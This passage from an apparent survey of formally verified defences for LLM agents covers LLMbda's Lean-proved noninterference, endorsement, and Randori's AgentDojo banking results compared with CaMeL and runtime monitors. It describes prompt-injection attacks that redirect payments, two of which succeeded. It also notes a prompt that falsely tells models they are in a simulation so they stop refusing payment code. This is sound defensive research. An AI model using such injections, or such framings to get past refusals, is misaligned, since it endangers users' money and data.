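C₀ ~ₘ C₁ ∧ e₀ ~ₘ e₁ ⇒ ⟦pc ⊢ C₀, e₀⟧ₘ ⌣ ⟦pc ⊢ C₁, e₁⟧ₘ

By the theorem, this holds for every level m and for all programs, conversations and models, where a model is any assignment of probabilities to responses. If a model always gives the same response to the same conversation, TIPNI reduces to the standard property for ordinary programs, which requires indistinguishable results whenever both runs finish.

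Garby and colleagues derived the definition, then found that Smith and Alpízar had proposed essentially the same property in 2011 for programs that flip coins, along with the bound on Δ. The new part is the proof for a language that generates and runs code. Lean checks the proof, which uses only Lean's three standard axioms, so unlike Lean4Agent, it adds no axiom about the model's behaviour.

The theorem covers one run at a time. If an ordinary Python loop restarted LLMbda programs after they stopped, it could leak a secret bit by bit, as CaMeL's retry loop can. An LLMbda program can't do this itself, because it can't catch a failed label check and continue.

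The observer in the theorem also sees only the final value and the final conversation, but the company that runs the model sees every prompt, including those in forks that the program later discards. The send rule allows a program to put a secret into a prompt, as long as the conversation's label records it. LLMbda's basic rules therefore let the model's provider see secrets, whereas tacit keeps them from the cloud model.

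### A second semantics that skips what the observer cannot see

Proving that two subdistributions are compatible requires finding a suitable ω. Garby and colleagues find it by defining a second way of running programs, the *skipping semantics*. It follows the normal rules until a computation's label goes beyond what an observer at level m can see. It then skips that computation and returns a dummy value that keeps the hidden label. If a later step calls the dummy value as a function, the semantics skips that call too.

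For example, when a program calls a function whose label is visible, the function's body runs as usual. If the function's label is not visible, the semantics evaluates the argument but skips the body. The full definition has 76 rules.

For an observer at {U}, the coin program runs normally until the coin lands tails and the program reaches `if secret`. That condition is labelled {S}, so the skipping semantics skips the whole inner branch and returns the coin. Heads and tails each have probability 0.5, whatever the secret is. This distribution is the ω that makes the program's two subdistributions compatible.

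Writing μ₀ and μ₁ for the normal subdistributions of two indistinguishable programs, and ω₀ and ω₁ for the ones with skipping, the proof needs three lemmas:

1. Skipping never makes an outcome less likely, so μ₀ ≤ ω₀ and μ₁ ≤ ω₁.
2. Skipping gives the same result for indistinguishable programs, so ω₀ = ω₁.
3. The probabilities with skipping add up to at most 1.

Together they give

μ₀ ≤ ω₀ = ω₁ ≥ μ₁,

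so the common value of ω₀ and ω₁ is the subdistribution that compatibility requires.

The first lemma holds because a skipped computation can't run forever or fail a check, so the program finishes at least as often as it would without skipping. The lemma also relies on confinement, which the check in the send rule enforces. Without confinement, a secret branch could add a prompt to a public conversation, and skipping the branch would omit that prompt and change the visible state. The second lemma holds because the two programs differ only in parts that don't affect execution under the skipping semantics.

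Smith and Alpízar's proof used a similar idea but deleted the secret parts from the program's text before running it. LLMbda's proof can't do that, because the model may write some of the program during the run, and some labels are known only then.

### Code that the model writes

When a program receives a response from the model, it parses the text and runs the result with pc equal to the conversation's label. Suppose the conversation contains an attacker's email and is labelled {U}. The attacker may get the model to respond with any program, but that program runs with pc = {U}, so every value it computes is untrusted and it can't add anything to a conversation labelled ∅.

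The theorem's only assumption about the parser is that it always turns the same text into the same code. Noninterference would still hold even if a bug in the parser turned a harmless response into a program that tries to email every secret to an attacker.

The proof doesn't depend on what the code in the model's response does. It compares two indistinguishable runs that have each reached a `recv`. If the observer can see the conversation, it is the same in both runs, so each possible response is equally likely in both. The parser turns the same response into the same code, so the runs stay indistinguishable. If the observer can't see the conversation, the code runs with a hidden label, and the skipping semantics passes over it.

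LLMbda's language rules update the labels on the model's code as it runs, so unlike Soteria, SPA and ELBA, LLMbda doesn't need to check the code before running it. The drawback is that a bad program may stop after doing part of its work.

The guarantee protects a tool only if the tool checks labels before it acts. In the reminder example, the tool for sending email requires a trusted subject and body. The privileged model wrote both before anyone read Bob's email, so they pass the check. By the theorem, changing Bob's email cannot alter the subject or body of any message that passes.

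The theorem gives no such protection to the recipient's address. The quarantined model extracted it from Bob's email, so it is untrusted, and the tool doesn't check it. Requiring a trusted address would stop the attacker from redirecting the reminder, but it would also stop the agent from replying to Bob unless the program explicitly relabeled the address as trusted, a step known as *endorsement*.

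## How LLMbda runs an agent, and at what cost

Suppose a user asks her agent to find a friend's payment details on his website and send him $50. The tool that reads web pages labels their contents untrusted, and the payment tool accepts only a trusted recipient. Here is a simplified plan, with labels on the right:

```
page    = read_url(site)                                {U}
account = quarantine("Find the account number", page)   {U}
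send_money(account, 50)                                 stops here
```

The check stops the payment even if nobody has tampered with the page. The label is accurate, because whoever controls the page chooses where the money goes. But the user asked the agent to rely on that page, so no model can complete this task under strict tracking.

LLMbda therefore has an `endorse` construct that relabels a value as trusted. If the last line of the plan sends the money to `endorse ∅ account` instead, the payment goes through. Anyone who reads the plan can see where outside data becomes trusted.

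### Endorsement and secrets

Endorsing a value must not also make it public. LLMbda splits each label into a trust part, which is U or nothing, and a secrecy part, which is S or nothing. Without the probabilities, the rule for a fixed target label t is:

```
pc ⊢ C, e ⇓ C′, l:v
───────────────────────────────────────────────────────────
pc ⊢ C, endorse t e ⇓ C′, (pc ⊔ ⟨trust(t), secrecy(l)⟩):v
```

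The result takes its trust part from the target and its secrecy part from the value's old label. The join with pc adds whatever influenced the decision to endorse. With ∅ as the target, the rule gives:

| Old label | pc | New label |
|---|---|---|
| {U} | ∅ | ∅ |
| {S} | ∅ | {S} |
| {U, S} | ∅ | {S} |
| {U} | {U} | {U} |

In the last row, the endorsement has no effect because the program reached it through untrusted data. If an attacker gets the model to return code that contains `endorse`, the code runs with pc = {U} and can't make anything trusted.

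This protection fails if an endorsement has marked the attacker's text as trusted and the program then turns that text into code. Garby and colleagues describe a wrapper that adds an extra mark to each endorsed value and refuses to endorse a value that already has one. They haven't proved what the wrapper guarantees.

Endorsement deliberately lets untrusted data influence trusted data, so noninterference no longer holds for trust. If an email says "general" in one run and "urgent" in another, an observer who sees only trusted data can't tell the runs apart until the program endorses the word. Noninterference still holds for secrets. Garby and colleagues prove in Lean that every program, including one that uses `endorse`, satisfies TIPNI at every level that includes U, where an observer sees both trusted and untrusted data. They call this *insulated TIPNI*. Secret inputs can't influence public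 outputs, except by making the program stop early or run forever, whatever an attacker writes and whatever the program endorses.

Endorsement can add or remove U but never removes S, so it can't make a hidden value visible to an observer at {U}. The noninterference theorem without endorsement is the special case in which labels have no trust part for `endorse` to change. Swapping the trust and secrecy parts gives the opposite construct, which releases a secret without making untrusted data trusted.

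### How much choice an attacker keeps

In one of Garby and colleagues' examples, an agent answers emails. A quarantined model sorts each email into one of a few fixed categories, and the agent uses the category as the subject of its reply. The mail tool requires a trusted subject, so the program endorses the category. An attacker who writes the email can influence which category the model picks but can't add a new one.

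With k yes-or-no decisions, one can distinguish 2ᵏ possibilities. A choice among n categories therefore gives the attacker at most

log₂ n bits

of influence, which is 2 bits for four categories and 3 bits for eight. The limit applies to each endorsement separately, so an attacker who writes ten emails can have up to ten times as much.

The idea comes from FIDES, which is described in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*. FIDES records each value's type in its label, such as a yes or no, an item from a fixed list, or free text. A policy can then accept an untrusted "yes" where it would reject an untrusted sentence. The number of bits in an answer doesn't measure the possible harm, though, because even a one-bit answer could lose the money if it decides whether to pay an invoice.

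A program that enforces the limit has to endorse the value v before checking it:

```
w = endorse ∅ v
if w is in [tag₁, …, tagₙ] then w else v
```

Checking v first would mean branching on untrusted data, and an endorsement inside that branch would have no effect. If w is not on the list, the program continues with v, which is still untrusted. Garby and colleagues have not formally proved the log₂ n bound for this construction.

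The method doesn't help with the friend's account number, because it could be anything. If the agent could pay only one of 16 payees the user had already saved, the attacker would have at most 4 bits of influence over the recipient and could redirect the money only to someone on that list.

### A proved interpreter with an unproved network call

*Operationalizing CaMeL* notes that the evidence for CaMeL's safeguards comes from benchmarks, and recommends modelling its interpreter in a proof assistant and proving noninterference. Garby and colleagues did this for their own language, and they run their agents on the same interpreter they proved correct.

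The interpreter, `peval`, is a Lean function. Lean supports proofs about an ordinary function only if the function always terminates, but an LLMbda program may run forever. `peval` therefore takes a step budget, called *fuel*, and stops when the fuel runs out. It also takes an oracle o, which supplies the model's answers.

One can picture the oracle as a book with an entry for every position in the run and every possible conversation. Suppose someone fills in each entry independently, at random, with the probabilities that the model gives to its answers in that conversation. The correctness theorem is then

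⟦pc ⊢ C, e⟧(C′, V) = Pr[for some fuel, peval(o, fuel, pc, C, e) ends with C′ and V].

The left side is the probability that the formal semantics gives to the final conversation C′ and value V. The right side is the probability that the interpreter reaches the same C′ and V with a randomly filled book. For the program that flips a coin twice, with a 0.3 chance of heads each time, a run reads two entries. The chance that they are heads and then tails is 0.3 × 0.7 = 0.21, as in the semantics.

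In a live run, the interpreter gets each entry from the model when it needs it. This gives the same probabilities as filling in the book beforehand, because a run never reads an entry twice. A live run has a fixed budget, so it may stop before the program finishes. Stopping early can only lower the probability of each outcome, so two compatible distributions stay compatible.

The network call is not verified. The `implemented_by` attribute makes the compiler replace the oracle with code that sends the conversation to the model's provider and returns the response, or an error message if the request fails. Lean's documentation warns that nothing checks whether the replacement is equivalent to the original. If the replacement returned the wrong text, it would behave like a different model, which the noninterference theorem covers. But the proofs don't rule out a replacement that also leaks secrets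 by copying every prompt to a public server.

### Practice on an artificial bank account

Models often need several attempts to write a working program, but retries are difficult to combine with labels. If a plan reads an untrusted file and fails, the error message may depend on the file. Adding that message to the conversation makes the conversation and every later plan untrusted. CaMeL avoids this by running its retry loop outside the labels, but this means it can leak a secret bit by bit.

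Garby and colleagues wrote an agent in LLMbda, Randori, that makes its mistakes on invented data instead. It is named after free sparring in Japanese martial arts. It works in four steps:

1. The model receives the task, the grammar of LLMbda, a description of the tools and an artificial bank account, and writes a plan.
2. The interpreter runs the plan on the artificial account. Tools that would move money change nothing, and every file contains the same placeholder sentence.
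3. If the plan fails, Randori adds the error message to the prompt and the model tries again, up to a fixed number of times.
4. In the same conversation, the model writes a final version, which the interpreter runs on the real account.

The error messages in step 3 come only from invented data, so they don't make the conversation untrusted. A plan that fails in the practice run also makes no real payment that the next attempt could repeat.

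A practice run can't show whether the plan would find the right amount in a real bill, because the placeholder file doesn't contain one. The final version is a rewrite, and Randori doesn't test it before the real run. Label checks also don't raise errors during practice, so a plan that violates a policy fails only in the real run, when it is too late to revise it.

The model also selects what to endorse while writing the plan, before the agent has read any real data, so injected text can't cause it to add an endorsement. But nothing prevents the model from endorsing too much by mistake.

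### Results on the banking tasks

Garby and colleagues tested Randori on the banking part of AgentDojo. In *AgentDojo*, Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024) built simulated environments in which ordinary code inspects the final state to decide whether the agent completed the user's task and whether the attacker succeeded. They avoided a language model judge because an injection might fool it too.

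The banking part has 11 tools, 16 user tasks and 9 attacks. One user task is to pay a bill stored in a text file, and one attack is to send as much money as possible to the attacker. Combining every task with every attack gives 144 pairs. Three repetitions gave each model 432 runs with attacks and 48 without.

Garby and colleagues also reran CaMeL with two of the three models, once with its policy checks on and once with them off. This table gives the percentage of user tasks completed, with 95% confidence intervals:

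| Agent | Model | No attack | Under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 75.0 ± 18.9 | 65.0 ± 6.7 |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 75.0 ± 20.0 | 63.4 ± 6.8 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 64.6 ± 22.0 | 59.5 ± 6.2 |
| Randori, no endorsement | Qwen3.7-plus | 62.5 ± 24.2 | 60.2 ± 7.2 |
| Randori, no endorsement | MiMo-v2.5 | 54.2 ± 23.3 | 56.2 ± 6.8 |
| CaMeL, checks off | GPT-5.2 | 66.7 ± 23.4 | 71.1 ± 7.7 |
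| CaMeL, checks off | MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8 ± 21.4 | 72.2 ± 7.4 |
| CaMeL, checks on | GPT-5.2 | 37.5 ± 26.6 | 30.0 ± 8.1 |
| CaMeL, checks on | MiMo-v2.5 | 37.5 ± 26.6 | 41.5 ± 7.9 |

Garby and colleagues conclude that Randori matches CaMeL without checks and completes roughly twice as many tasks as CaMeL with them. The claim of a match is weak because, with only 16 tasks, the intervals are so wide that a ten-point difference could easily go unnoticed. Under attack, CaMeL without checks did better than Randori with both models, by 6 points with GPT-5.2 and 13 with MiMo, but many of its runs didn't finish and the table counts only those that did.

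There is better evidence that Randori completes more tasks than CaMeL with checks. The intervals overlap without an attack, but under attack they are far apart for GPT-5.2 and still do not overlap for MiMo.

Endorsement explains only part of this advantage. With MiMo and no attack, Randori completed 31 of 48 runs with endorsement and 26 without it, while CaMeL with checks completed 18. Endorsement therefore accounts for 5 of Randori's 13 additional runs. Some of the other 8 may be due to differences in policy, because Garby and colleagues implemented only some of CaMeL's policies and made those less strict.

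Other systems, like CaMeL, complete fewer tasks with their policies on, as ELBA's results on AgentDojo's Slack tasks showed. Garby and colleagues cite a test on 21 of those tasks in which Zhou and colleagues' library completed 8 with policies on, and CaMeL completed 7.

### What stopped the attacks

Garby and colleagues divide the 144 pairs into two groups. In 97 of them, the attack needs a tool call or file that a plan for the user's task would never include, such as a payment when the user wants a summary of recent transactions. A plan written in advance stops these attacks without any labels. In the remaining 47 pairs, the plan could serve the attacker as well as the user. This table shows how many attacks failed:

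| Agent | Model | Plan can't serve the attack | Plan could serve it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 291 of 291 | 139 of 141 |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 291 of 291 | 141 of 141 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 291 of 291 | 141 of 141 |
| CaMeL, checks off | GPT-5.2 | 98 of 99 | 141 of 141 |
| CaMeL, checks off | MiMo-v2.5 | 240 of 241 | 138 of 141 |
| CaMeL, checks on | GPT-5.2 | 97 of 97 | 134 of 134 |
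| CaMeL, checks on | MiMo-v2.5 | 216 of 216 | 141 of 141 |

Repetitions of the same pair aren't independent, so the confidence intervals are based on the number of pairs. For a perfect record on n pairs, the lower end of the 95% interval is n / (n + 1.96²), which is 92.4% for 47 pairs and 96.2% for 97. Randori with GPT-5.2 has an interval of 90.0% to 99.8% on the 47 harder pairs.

These results are weak evidence that labels stop attacks, because CaMeL without checks also resisted 617 of the 622 attacks, which left only five for the labels to stop.

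Two of its five failures are in the group where the plan should have been enough. The user asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely, and the model wrote a plan with a loop that could call any tool the file named. An attacker who controlled the file could choose the agent's actions, even though the plan was complete before the agent read anything. CaMeL's policy checks would normally protect against such a plan.

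### The two attacks that succeeded

Randori failed twice in 1,296 runs, both times with GPT-5.2 on the same pair of user task and attack. The user asked the agent to read a text file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The plan extracted the payment details, endorsed them and paid the attacker.

This is consistent with the theorem that endorsement can't release secrets, because no secret leaked. Untrusted data influenced a payment, which the endorsement in the plan allowed. Without endorsement, Randori blocks the attack, but it also can't pay a genuine bill from a file.

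*Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) criticises this feature of AgentDojo, using the example of a task to pay a bill from a file. When an injection overwrites the file, the original bill is gone, so no agent can complete the task, and the scores for tasks completed under attack fall whatever the defence. The file also no longer shows which payment the user wanted. According to Garby and colleagues, one of the two successful attacks in CaMeL's original evaluation was the same case, and CaMeL's designers put it outside their threat model.

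Randori ran each pair three times per model, and with GPT-5.2 this attack succeeded in two of the three runs. An attacker who can edit a bill will choose this attack over the ones that fail, so the overall rate of two failures in 1,296 runs understates how common it would be in practice.

### How far the evidence goes

Garby and colleagues have tested Randori only on banking, one of AgentDojo's four environments. Their bank is a data structure inside the LLMbda program, and each tool is an LLMbda function that returns a new version of it. A real payment service would be outside both the language and the proof. Because models otherwise often refused to write code that makes payments, the prompt begins by telling the model that it is in a simulation with no real money, which would be false at a real bank.

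The policies have gaps that the theorem doesn't address. In the published list of tools, only file contents are labeled untrusted. Transaction histories are not, although strangers can write the subject lines of payments they send. The payment-scheduling tool requires a trusted amount but not a trusted recipient. If the code matches the list, an attacker could influence who receives a scheduled payment without the plan endorsing anything.

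CaMeL's scores come from a rerun by the designers of a competing system, and its performance depends on the setup. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) found that CaMeL needs tool descriptions that specify the format of each result, because the model has to write code that processes a result before seeing one. AgentDojo's descriptions omit the format. Randori is also at a disadvantage, because no model was trained on LLMbda and its prompt has to include the whole grammar and fourteen rules about common mistakes.

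The attacks were also fixed in advance. Debenedetti and colleagues warn that it is easy to build a defence against any specific attack, and they intended AgentDojo to be extended with attacks designed for each new defence. For Randori, such an attack would target the values that its plans endorse, since the label checks no longer protect those values.

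## Which properties can be checked, and when

LLMbda's noninterference theorem is about a harder kind of property than the other systems' proofs, but it doesn't replace them. An LLMbda program that always emails Alice the same public summary twice satisfies noninterference, while Agenra would stop the second email with a simple counter. This table compares the systems:

| System | Property proved | When the check happens | Proof tool | Does the proof cover running code? | Assumption about the model |
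|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| PocketFlow | reads only in the workspace, calls only listed tools, limited steps | at each action | Dafny | generated Python, if Dafny's compiler is correct | returns a typed action |
| Mashin | some check comes before any I/O | once for the language | Rocq | unclear; random tests link model and software | none |
| Cedar | no access without a permit or against a forbid | at each call, with policy analysis beforehand | Lean, SMT solver | no; random tests compare Lean with Rust | none |
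| Agenra | every admitted call obeys the rules on labels, origins, recipients and quotas | at each call | Lean | the Lean core, not the Python around it | none |
| Soteria | every path through the plan obeys the rules | before the run, then at each call | Dafny | the plan, not the monitor | meets conditions that Soteria checks during the run |
| Lean4Agent | the steps' contracts fit together | before the run | Lean | no | fulfils every contract |
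| λ_A | typed programs don't get stuck, and loops end | before the run | Rocq | no | always returns, with fixed answers |
| ELBA | agent calls preserve what the host language's types guarantee | before each generated program runs | proof on paper | no | any fixed function |
| tacit | code can use only the capabilities in its type | before each generated program runs | proof assistants, for the core type system | no | none for the cloud model; the local model is trusted |
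| LLMbda | noninterference, unless the program stops early or never ends | once for the language, with labels updated at each step | Lean | the interpreter, not the network call | answers depend only on the conversation |

Agenra and LLMbda can run the same code they verify because Lean is both a programming language and a proof assistant. *LEANGUARD* likewise runs the rules it verifies. It checks all its proofs when a developer builds the policy, so only the compiled rules have to run at each tool call.

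### What a monitor can enforce

Cedar, Agenra and Soteria's monitor decide during the run, when they can use what has happened so far but not what comes next. In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider worked out which policies such a monitor can enforce if all it can do is stop a program before a bad step.

The monitor sees one run, so its policy has to judge each run separately. Let p(σ) mean that the policy accepts the run σ. Since the monitor can't see the future, rejecting an unfinished run τ also rules out everything that could have followed it. It also has to reject a bad run after finitely many steps:

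```
not p(τ)  ⇒  not p(τ followed by σ), for every σ
not p(σ)  ⇒  not p(first i steps of σ), for some i
```

A policy that meets these conditions is a safety property. "At most one send" meets them, because a run with a second send violates the policy no matter what follows.

A policy that must reject every continuation of a run it rejects cannot guarantee that Alice gets the summary. After Read and Sanitize, the agent has not yet sent an email. If the policy rejects this unfinished run, it must also reject the successful run that begins the same way. If it accepts the unfinished run, the agent can stop there without sending Alice the summary.

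In Schneider's similar example about a shop, a monitor can block everything the shop does after a customer pays except deliver the goods, but it can't stop the shop from doing nothing. Soteria's rule that an agent must read a file back after writing it has the same problem, which Soteria avoids by checking the whole plan in advance. Schneider's result doesn't cover compilers and theorem provers, which can examine all of a program's possible runs, or monitors that can insert actions, which could read the file themselves.

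A monitor also needs enough memory. Schneider describes monitors as automata, which move between states as they observe actions. For the report task, two states are enough:

```
unsent:  Send → sent          any other action → unsent
sent:    Send → not allowed   any other action → sent
```

With fixed policies and data, Cedar is an automaton with a single state, so it can't distinguish the first send from the second. Agenra's ledgers and Dogwood's log of earlier calls add the states needed to do this.

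### Properties of several runs

Suppose the report has a secret field that records whether the company plans layoffs. An agent reads the report and emails the public summary only if layoffs are planned:

| Secret field | Trace |
|---|---|
| layoffs | Read, Sanitize, Lookup, Extract, Send |
| no layoffs | Read, Sanitize, Lookup, Extract |

Neither trace breaks a rule of the report task. The email contains only public text, goes to Alice and goes out once. But if Alice knows how the agent works, she learns the secret from whether she gets an email.

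No monitor that judges traces one at a time can distinguish this agent from a harmless one, because the leak lies in the difference between the two traces. A harmless agent that always sends the summary also produces the first trace, and one that never sends it produces the second.

Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, give the general definition. Let T be the set of all traces a system can produce. A trace property P is a set of acceptable traces, while a *hyperproperty* H is a set of acceptable sets of traces:

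```
T satisfies P  if  T ⊆ P
T satisfies H  if  T ∈ H
```

Noninterference is a hyperproperty, because whether one trace is acceptable depends on which others the system can produce.

Agenra's confidentiality theorem applies to each trace separately. Under its assumptions, no email contains data from a confidential source unless the data passed through a trusted release such as Sanitize. Shivakumar and colleagues state that this isn't noninterference. Agenra would allow both traces in the table.

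LLMbda's labels also follow one run at a time, yet they guarantee noninterference. This doesn't contradict Schneider, who points out that a monitor can enforce a stricter safety property that implies the absence of leaks. The price is that it also stops harmless programs, such as this one:

```
if secret then @"Hello" else @"Hello"
```

Both branches send the same prompt, so nothing leaks. If the conversation is public, LLMbda stops the program anyway, because the send is inside a secret branch. The Send in the layoffs example is also inside a secret branch, so a mail tool that accepts only public inputs would reject it.

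Strict noninterference could make even the honest version of the report task impossible, because if the whole report has the label {S}, so does any summary of it. But LLMbda labels each field of a record separately, so a developer can mark only the secret fields. Code that selects only the other fields then produces a public summary without having to release a secret.

If the model always gives the same answer to the same conversation, two finite runs are enough to refute LLMbda's noninterference. Clarkson and Schneider call this kind of hyperproperty *2-safety* and prove that one can check it as an ordinary safety property of two copies of the system running side by side. For the report task, the copies would start with the same public fields and different secret ones, and their visible results would have to match whenever both finish. Soteria's plans look suitable for this method, since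 Dafny already checks safety properties of single plans. If the model answers at random, two runs may differ by chance, so LLMbda compares probabilities instead.

Logics for stating hyperproperties and algorithms for checking them, including by monitoring, exist outside the agent field. *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties* (Finkbeiner, 2025) reviews both.

### Why languages are small or checks cautious

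A check can reject a bad program before it runs, but Rice's theorem (1953) limits how accurate such a check can be. If some programs in a general-purpose language such as Python have a behavioral property and others lack it, no algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether it has that property.

For the report task, suppose a checker could always tell whether a program will send the raw report. Take any program p that sends no email, and add a line:

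```
run p
Send(raw report)
```

The new program sends the raw report if and only if p finishes. The checker could therefore decide whether any such p finishes, which Alan Turing proved impossible in 1936.

SPA and Cedar avoid the problem by leaving open-ended loops out of the language. ELBA keeps a general-purpose language, and its type checker is cautious instead. If only text of type `Clean` may go into an email, the compiler rejects this program, although the forbidden branch never runs:

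```
if 1 = 2 then Send(raw) else Send(clean)
```

Soteria combines both approaches. Its plans have no cycles, but Dafny may still fail to prove that a correct plan is safe. Monitoring is easier because a monitor only has to check the current call.

Every program in LLMbda, a general-purpose language, provably satisfies noninterference, because the language's rules stop any run that would violate it. This is consistent with Rice's theorem, which applies only to properties that some programs lack. Mashin works the same way, since its operator Gov adds checks to every program.

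McCann uses Rice's theorem in a pen-and-paper proof that a workflow system needs an opaque component, in practice a language model, because no ordinary program can answer every question about what programs do. The argument fails because a language model is also a program, so the theorem limits it too. A model may make good guesses, but Rice's theorem gives no reason to expect that.

### Termination, cost and useful completion

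Schneider notes that removing runs from a system never makes it violate a safety property, so an agent that refuses every call always passes a safety check. LLMbda's noninterference has the same weakness, because a program that always stops early passes by producing no results to compare. Under McCann's definition, Mashin's endless loop after a denied request is also safe.

**Termination.** A limit of 20 steps per run is a safety property, and a counter can enforce it. Even with the limit, the agent finishes only if each step finishes, as with λ_A's loops. The requirement that an agent eventually stops is not a safety property, because an agent that is still running may stop later.

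Limits in seconds are harder to enforce than limits in steps. "Alice waits at most 60 seconds" is a safety property, since a violation can be detected once 60 seconds have passed, but a monitor can't enforce it because stopping the agent doesn't stop the clock. Schneider uses an example like this to show that monitors that can only stop the agent can't enforce some safety properties. Such a monitor can block any email after five o'clock, but it can't ensure that the agent sends one before then.

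**Cost.** A monitor can enforce a spending cap if it has an upper bound on the cost of the next call. If the cap is 20 cents, the agent has spent 17, and the next call costs at most 4, the monitor has to block the call, even though it might have cost only 1 cent. By the time the bill arrived, the agent could already have exceeded the cap.

A limit on average cost is a different kind of property because it depends on all of a system's runs. Clarkson and Schneider discuss average response time, and the same reasoning applies to money. One run that costs a dollar doesn't violate an average of 10 cents, because enough cheap runs can bring the average down. A monitor could enforce the limit by capping every run at 10 cents, but this would stop expensive runs that the limit allows.

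The weakest version of **useful completion** is that at least one run delivers the summary. One example proves this, and Agenra uses a bounded search to look for one. Finding one doesn't guarantee that an agent will deliver the summary.

An attacker can also prevent delivery without breaking a rule. In Agenra's report policy, Sanitize has a quota of one. An injected agent can sanitize the attacker's text first, which uses up the quota, so the report can't be sanitized. Shivakumar and colleagues describe an extra rule that Sanitize accepts only the result of Read. Agenra then rejects the call on the attacker's text without counting it against the quota, so the stricter policy makes the agent more useful by keeping the quota available for the report.

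The strongest version is that every run delivers the summary. No system can prove this while the model can do anything, because the model might never request a send. But the report task doesn't need a model once a plan exists, since all five operations are ordinary code. A fixed plan that performs them in order will deliver the summary if every tool succeeds and the rules allow every call. One could prove this for a particular plan, under assumptions about the directory and the mail server.

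When the model has to make decisions during the run, only trials can show whether the agent is useful. Dantas and colleagues recommend measuring the *safe success rate*, the share of all tasks that an agent completes correctly without violating a rule. They report a study on τ-Bench, a benchmark of customer service tasks, in which a monitor blocked 94% of unsafe actions. In most settings, the agents still completed fewer than 5% of tasks both safely and correctly, because they found other unsafe routes.

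This result, which Dantas and colleagues call the *verifier tax*, comes from a single study, and later evidence suggests that the effect can be smaller. Soteria's agents completed between 35% and 90% of the airline and retail tasks in τ²-bench without breaking a rule. The benchmarks and models differ, so the numbers aren't directly comparable. Soteria also gives the agent a plan and tells it which call is missing, so the agent is less likely to have to search for another route after a refusal.

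### Combining the guarantees

Safety properties are easy to combine. Schneider shows that several monitors used together enforce all their policies, because a call goes through only if every monitor allows it. For the report task, PocketFlow could check the tool, Cedar the recipient and Agenra the quota.

The order of the checks still affects usefulness. Agenra should run last, because if it counts an email against the agent's limit of one and Cedar then denies that email, the agent can't send another.

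Shivakumar and colleagues prove a combined guarantee of this kind within Agenra. With one-time approvals switched on, every email that Agenra admits has a public body produced by Sanitize, goes to the address from the directory and uses up an approval for exactly that call. At most one such email goes out, even if the mail server fails. The proof assumes, among other things, that the labels, Sanitize and the directory are correct. The parts can be combined because they are all safety properties and Agenra's monitor keeps the records needed to enforce them.

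Adding noninterference is harder, partly because the proofs represent the model differently. Moon and Varshney let the model return any action at any step, which works well for safety but would make almost every agent fail noninterference. Suppose an agent passes on the model's answer to a question unrelated to the secret. In two runs with different secrets, the model may answer "yes" in one and "no" in the other, so the results differ even though the secret didn't influence them. LLMbda therefore compares runs that use the same model with the same probabilities.

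Refinement causes another conflict, because Clarkson and Schneider show that a concrete system can leak a secret by doing less than the abstract one allows. Suppose the abstract agent may send the summary either as plain text or as an attachment, whatever the report says. A concrete agent that uses an attachment only when layoffs are planned does nothing the abstract agent couldn't do, but it reveals whether they are planned. The problem doesn't arise for 2-safety properties, because removing runs can't create a pair that violates the property. Garby and colleagues avoid it by proving that their interpreter gives each outcome the same probability as the formal semantics.

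Quotas can also leak information. Suppose an agent may look up Alice's address only once, and a program uses that lookup early on only if layoffs are planned. When the program later tries the lookup in public code, a refusal reveals that the quota has been used up and therefore that layoffs are planned. The labels don't capture this leak if the monitor returns the refusal as public text.

LLMbda's theorem would still hold if a refusal stopped the whole program, for the same reason that it holds with a limited step budget. However, someone who notices that the program stopped could learn the secret.

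An LLMbda program could also track the quota. If the counter is an ordinary value, LLMbda labels it automatically, and a refusal that depends on a secret is labelled secret. The noninterference theorem would cover the resulting program without a new proof. "At most one send" would need its own proof about the function that sends mail, including that code written by the model can't reset the counter or bypass the function.

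Guaranteed termination would strengthen LLMbda's theorem. If every loop were bounded, as in λ_A, and every call returned, a secret could affect the results only through runs stopped by label checks. λ_A's static types would be harder to add because LLMbda runs code that the model writes during execution. Each response would need a type check before it runs, as in ELBA.

ELBA is the published system that comes closest to joining these approaches, since it combines typed agent calls with a library that tracks labels at run time. Its transfer theorem covers noninterference wherever the host language's types guarantee it, but does not cover what the program sends to the model. No published theorem appears to join two of the systems in the table.

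As future work, Moon and Varshney propose combining their guarantee about actions with statistical limits on how often a model's text is unacceptable. For the report task, the result might be that email goes only to Alice and that at most 2% of her summaries contain an error. The restriction on email would hold for any input, but the error rate would hold only for inputs like those in the tests, and an attacker can choose different ones.

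## What stays outside the verified core

Even a theorem that combined all these guarantees would cover only what its designers put in the formal model. For Agenra, Shivakumar and colleagues list unproved code, the developer's declarations, the tools and the people who approve calls as outside the proofs.

Defenders of such systems usually argue that the unproved part is small and written down, so people can audit it. This argument is convincing when the unproved part is a few hundred lines of connecting code, but much less so when it includes assumptions about a reviewer's judgement or a program's running time.

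### Rules that miss what the user meant

Councilman, Fu and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Formal Verification of LLM-Generated Code from Natural Language Prompts*, describe the first gap with two sets. U contains every program that would do what the user wants, and ⟦s⟧ contains every program that satisfies the formal specification s. A specification usually leaves some details open, so even a good one gives only

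U ⊆ ⟦s⟧.

A verifier can show that a program belongs to ⟦s⟧, but not that it belongs to U, because only the user knows what U is. A program in ⟦s⟧ but not in U passes verification and does the wrong thing. In the report task, if the company has two employees called Alice and the policy looks up the wrong one, Agenra would enforce the policy perfectly and the wrong Alice would get the summary.

Language models can write specifications, but not yet reliably. *VeriBench* (Miranda, Daruru and colleagues, 2026) gave coding agents Python programs and had them write Lean versions, with theorems about what each program should do and proofs of those theorems. A language model then rated from 0 to 1 how closely the theorems matched reference theorems that people had reviewed.

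| System | Files that typecheck | Stated theorems proved | Estimated equivalence |
|---|---|---|---|
| Codex (GPT-5.4) | 100% | 23.7% | 0.102 |
| Claude Code (Sonnet 4.6) | 100% | 11.4% | 0.098 |
| One call to Sonnet 4.6 | 31.0% | 28.2% | 0.105 |
| Gemini 3 Flash (preview) | 20.6% | 4.3% | 0.156 |
| Leanstral v2 | 29.2% | 6.5% | 0.058 |

A file can typecheck without complete proofs because Lean accepts `sorry` in place of a proof. So Codex and Claude Code produced valid Lean every time, but their theorems rarely matched the reference.

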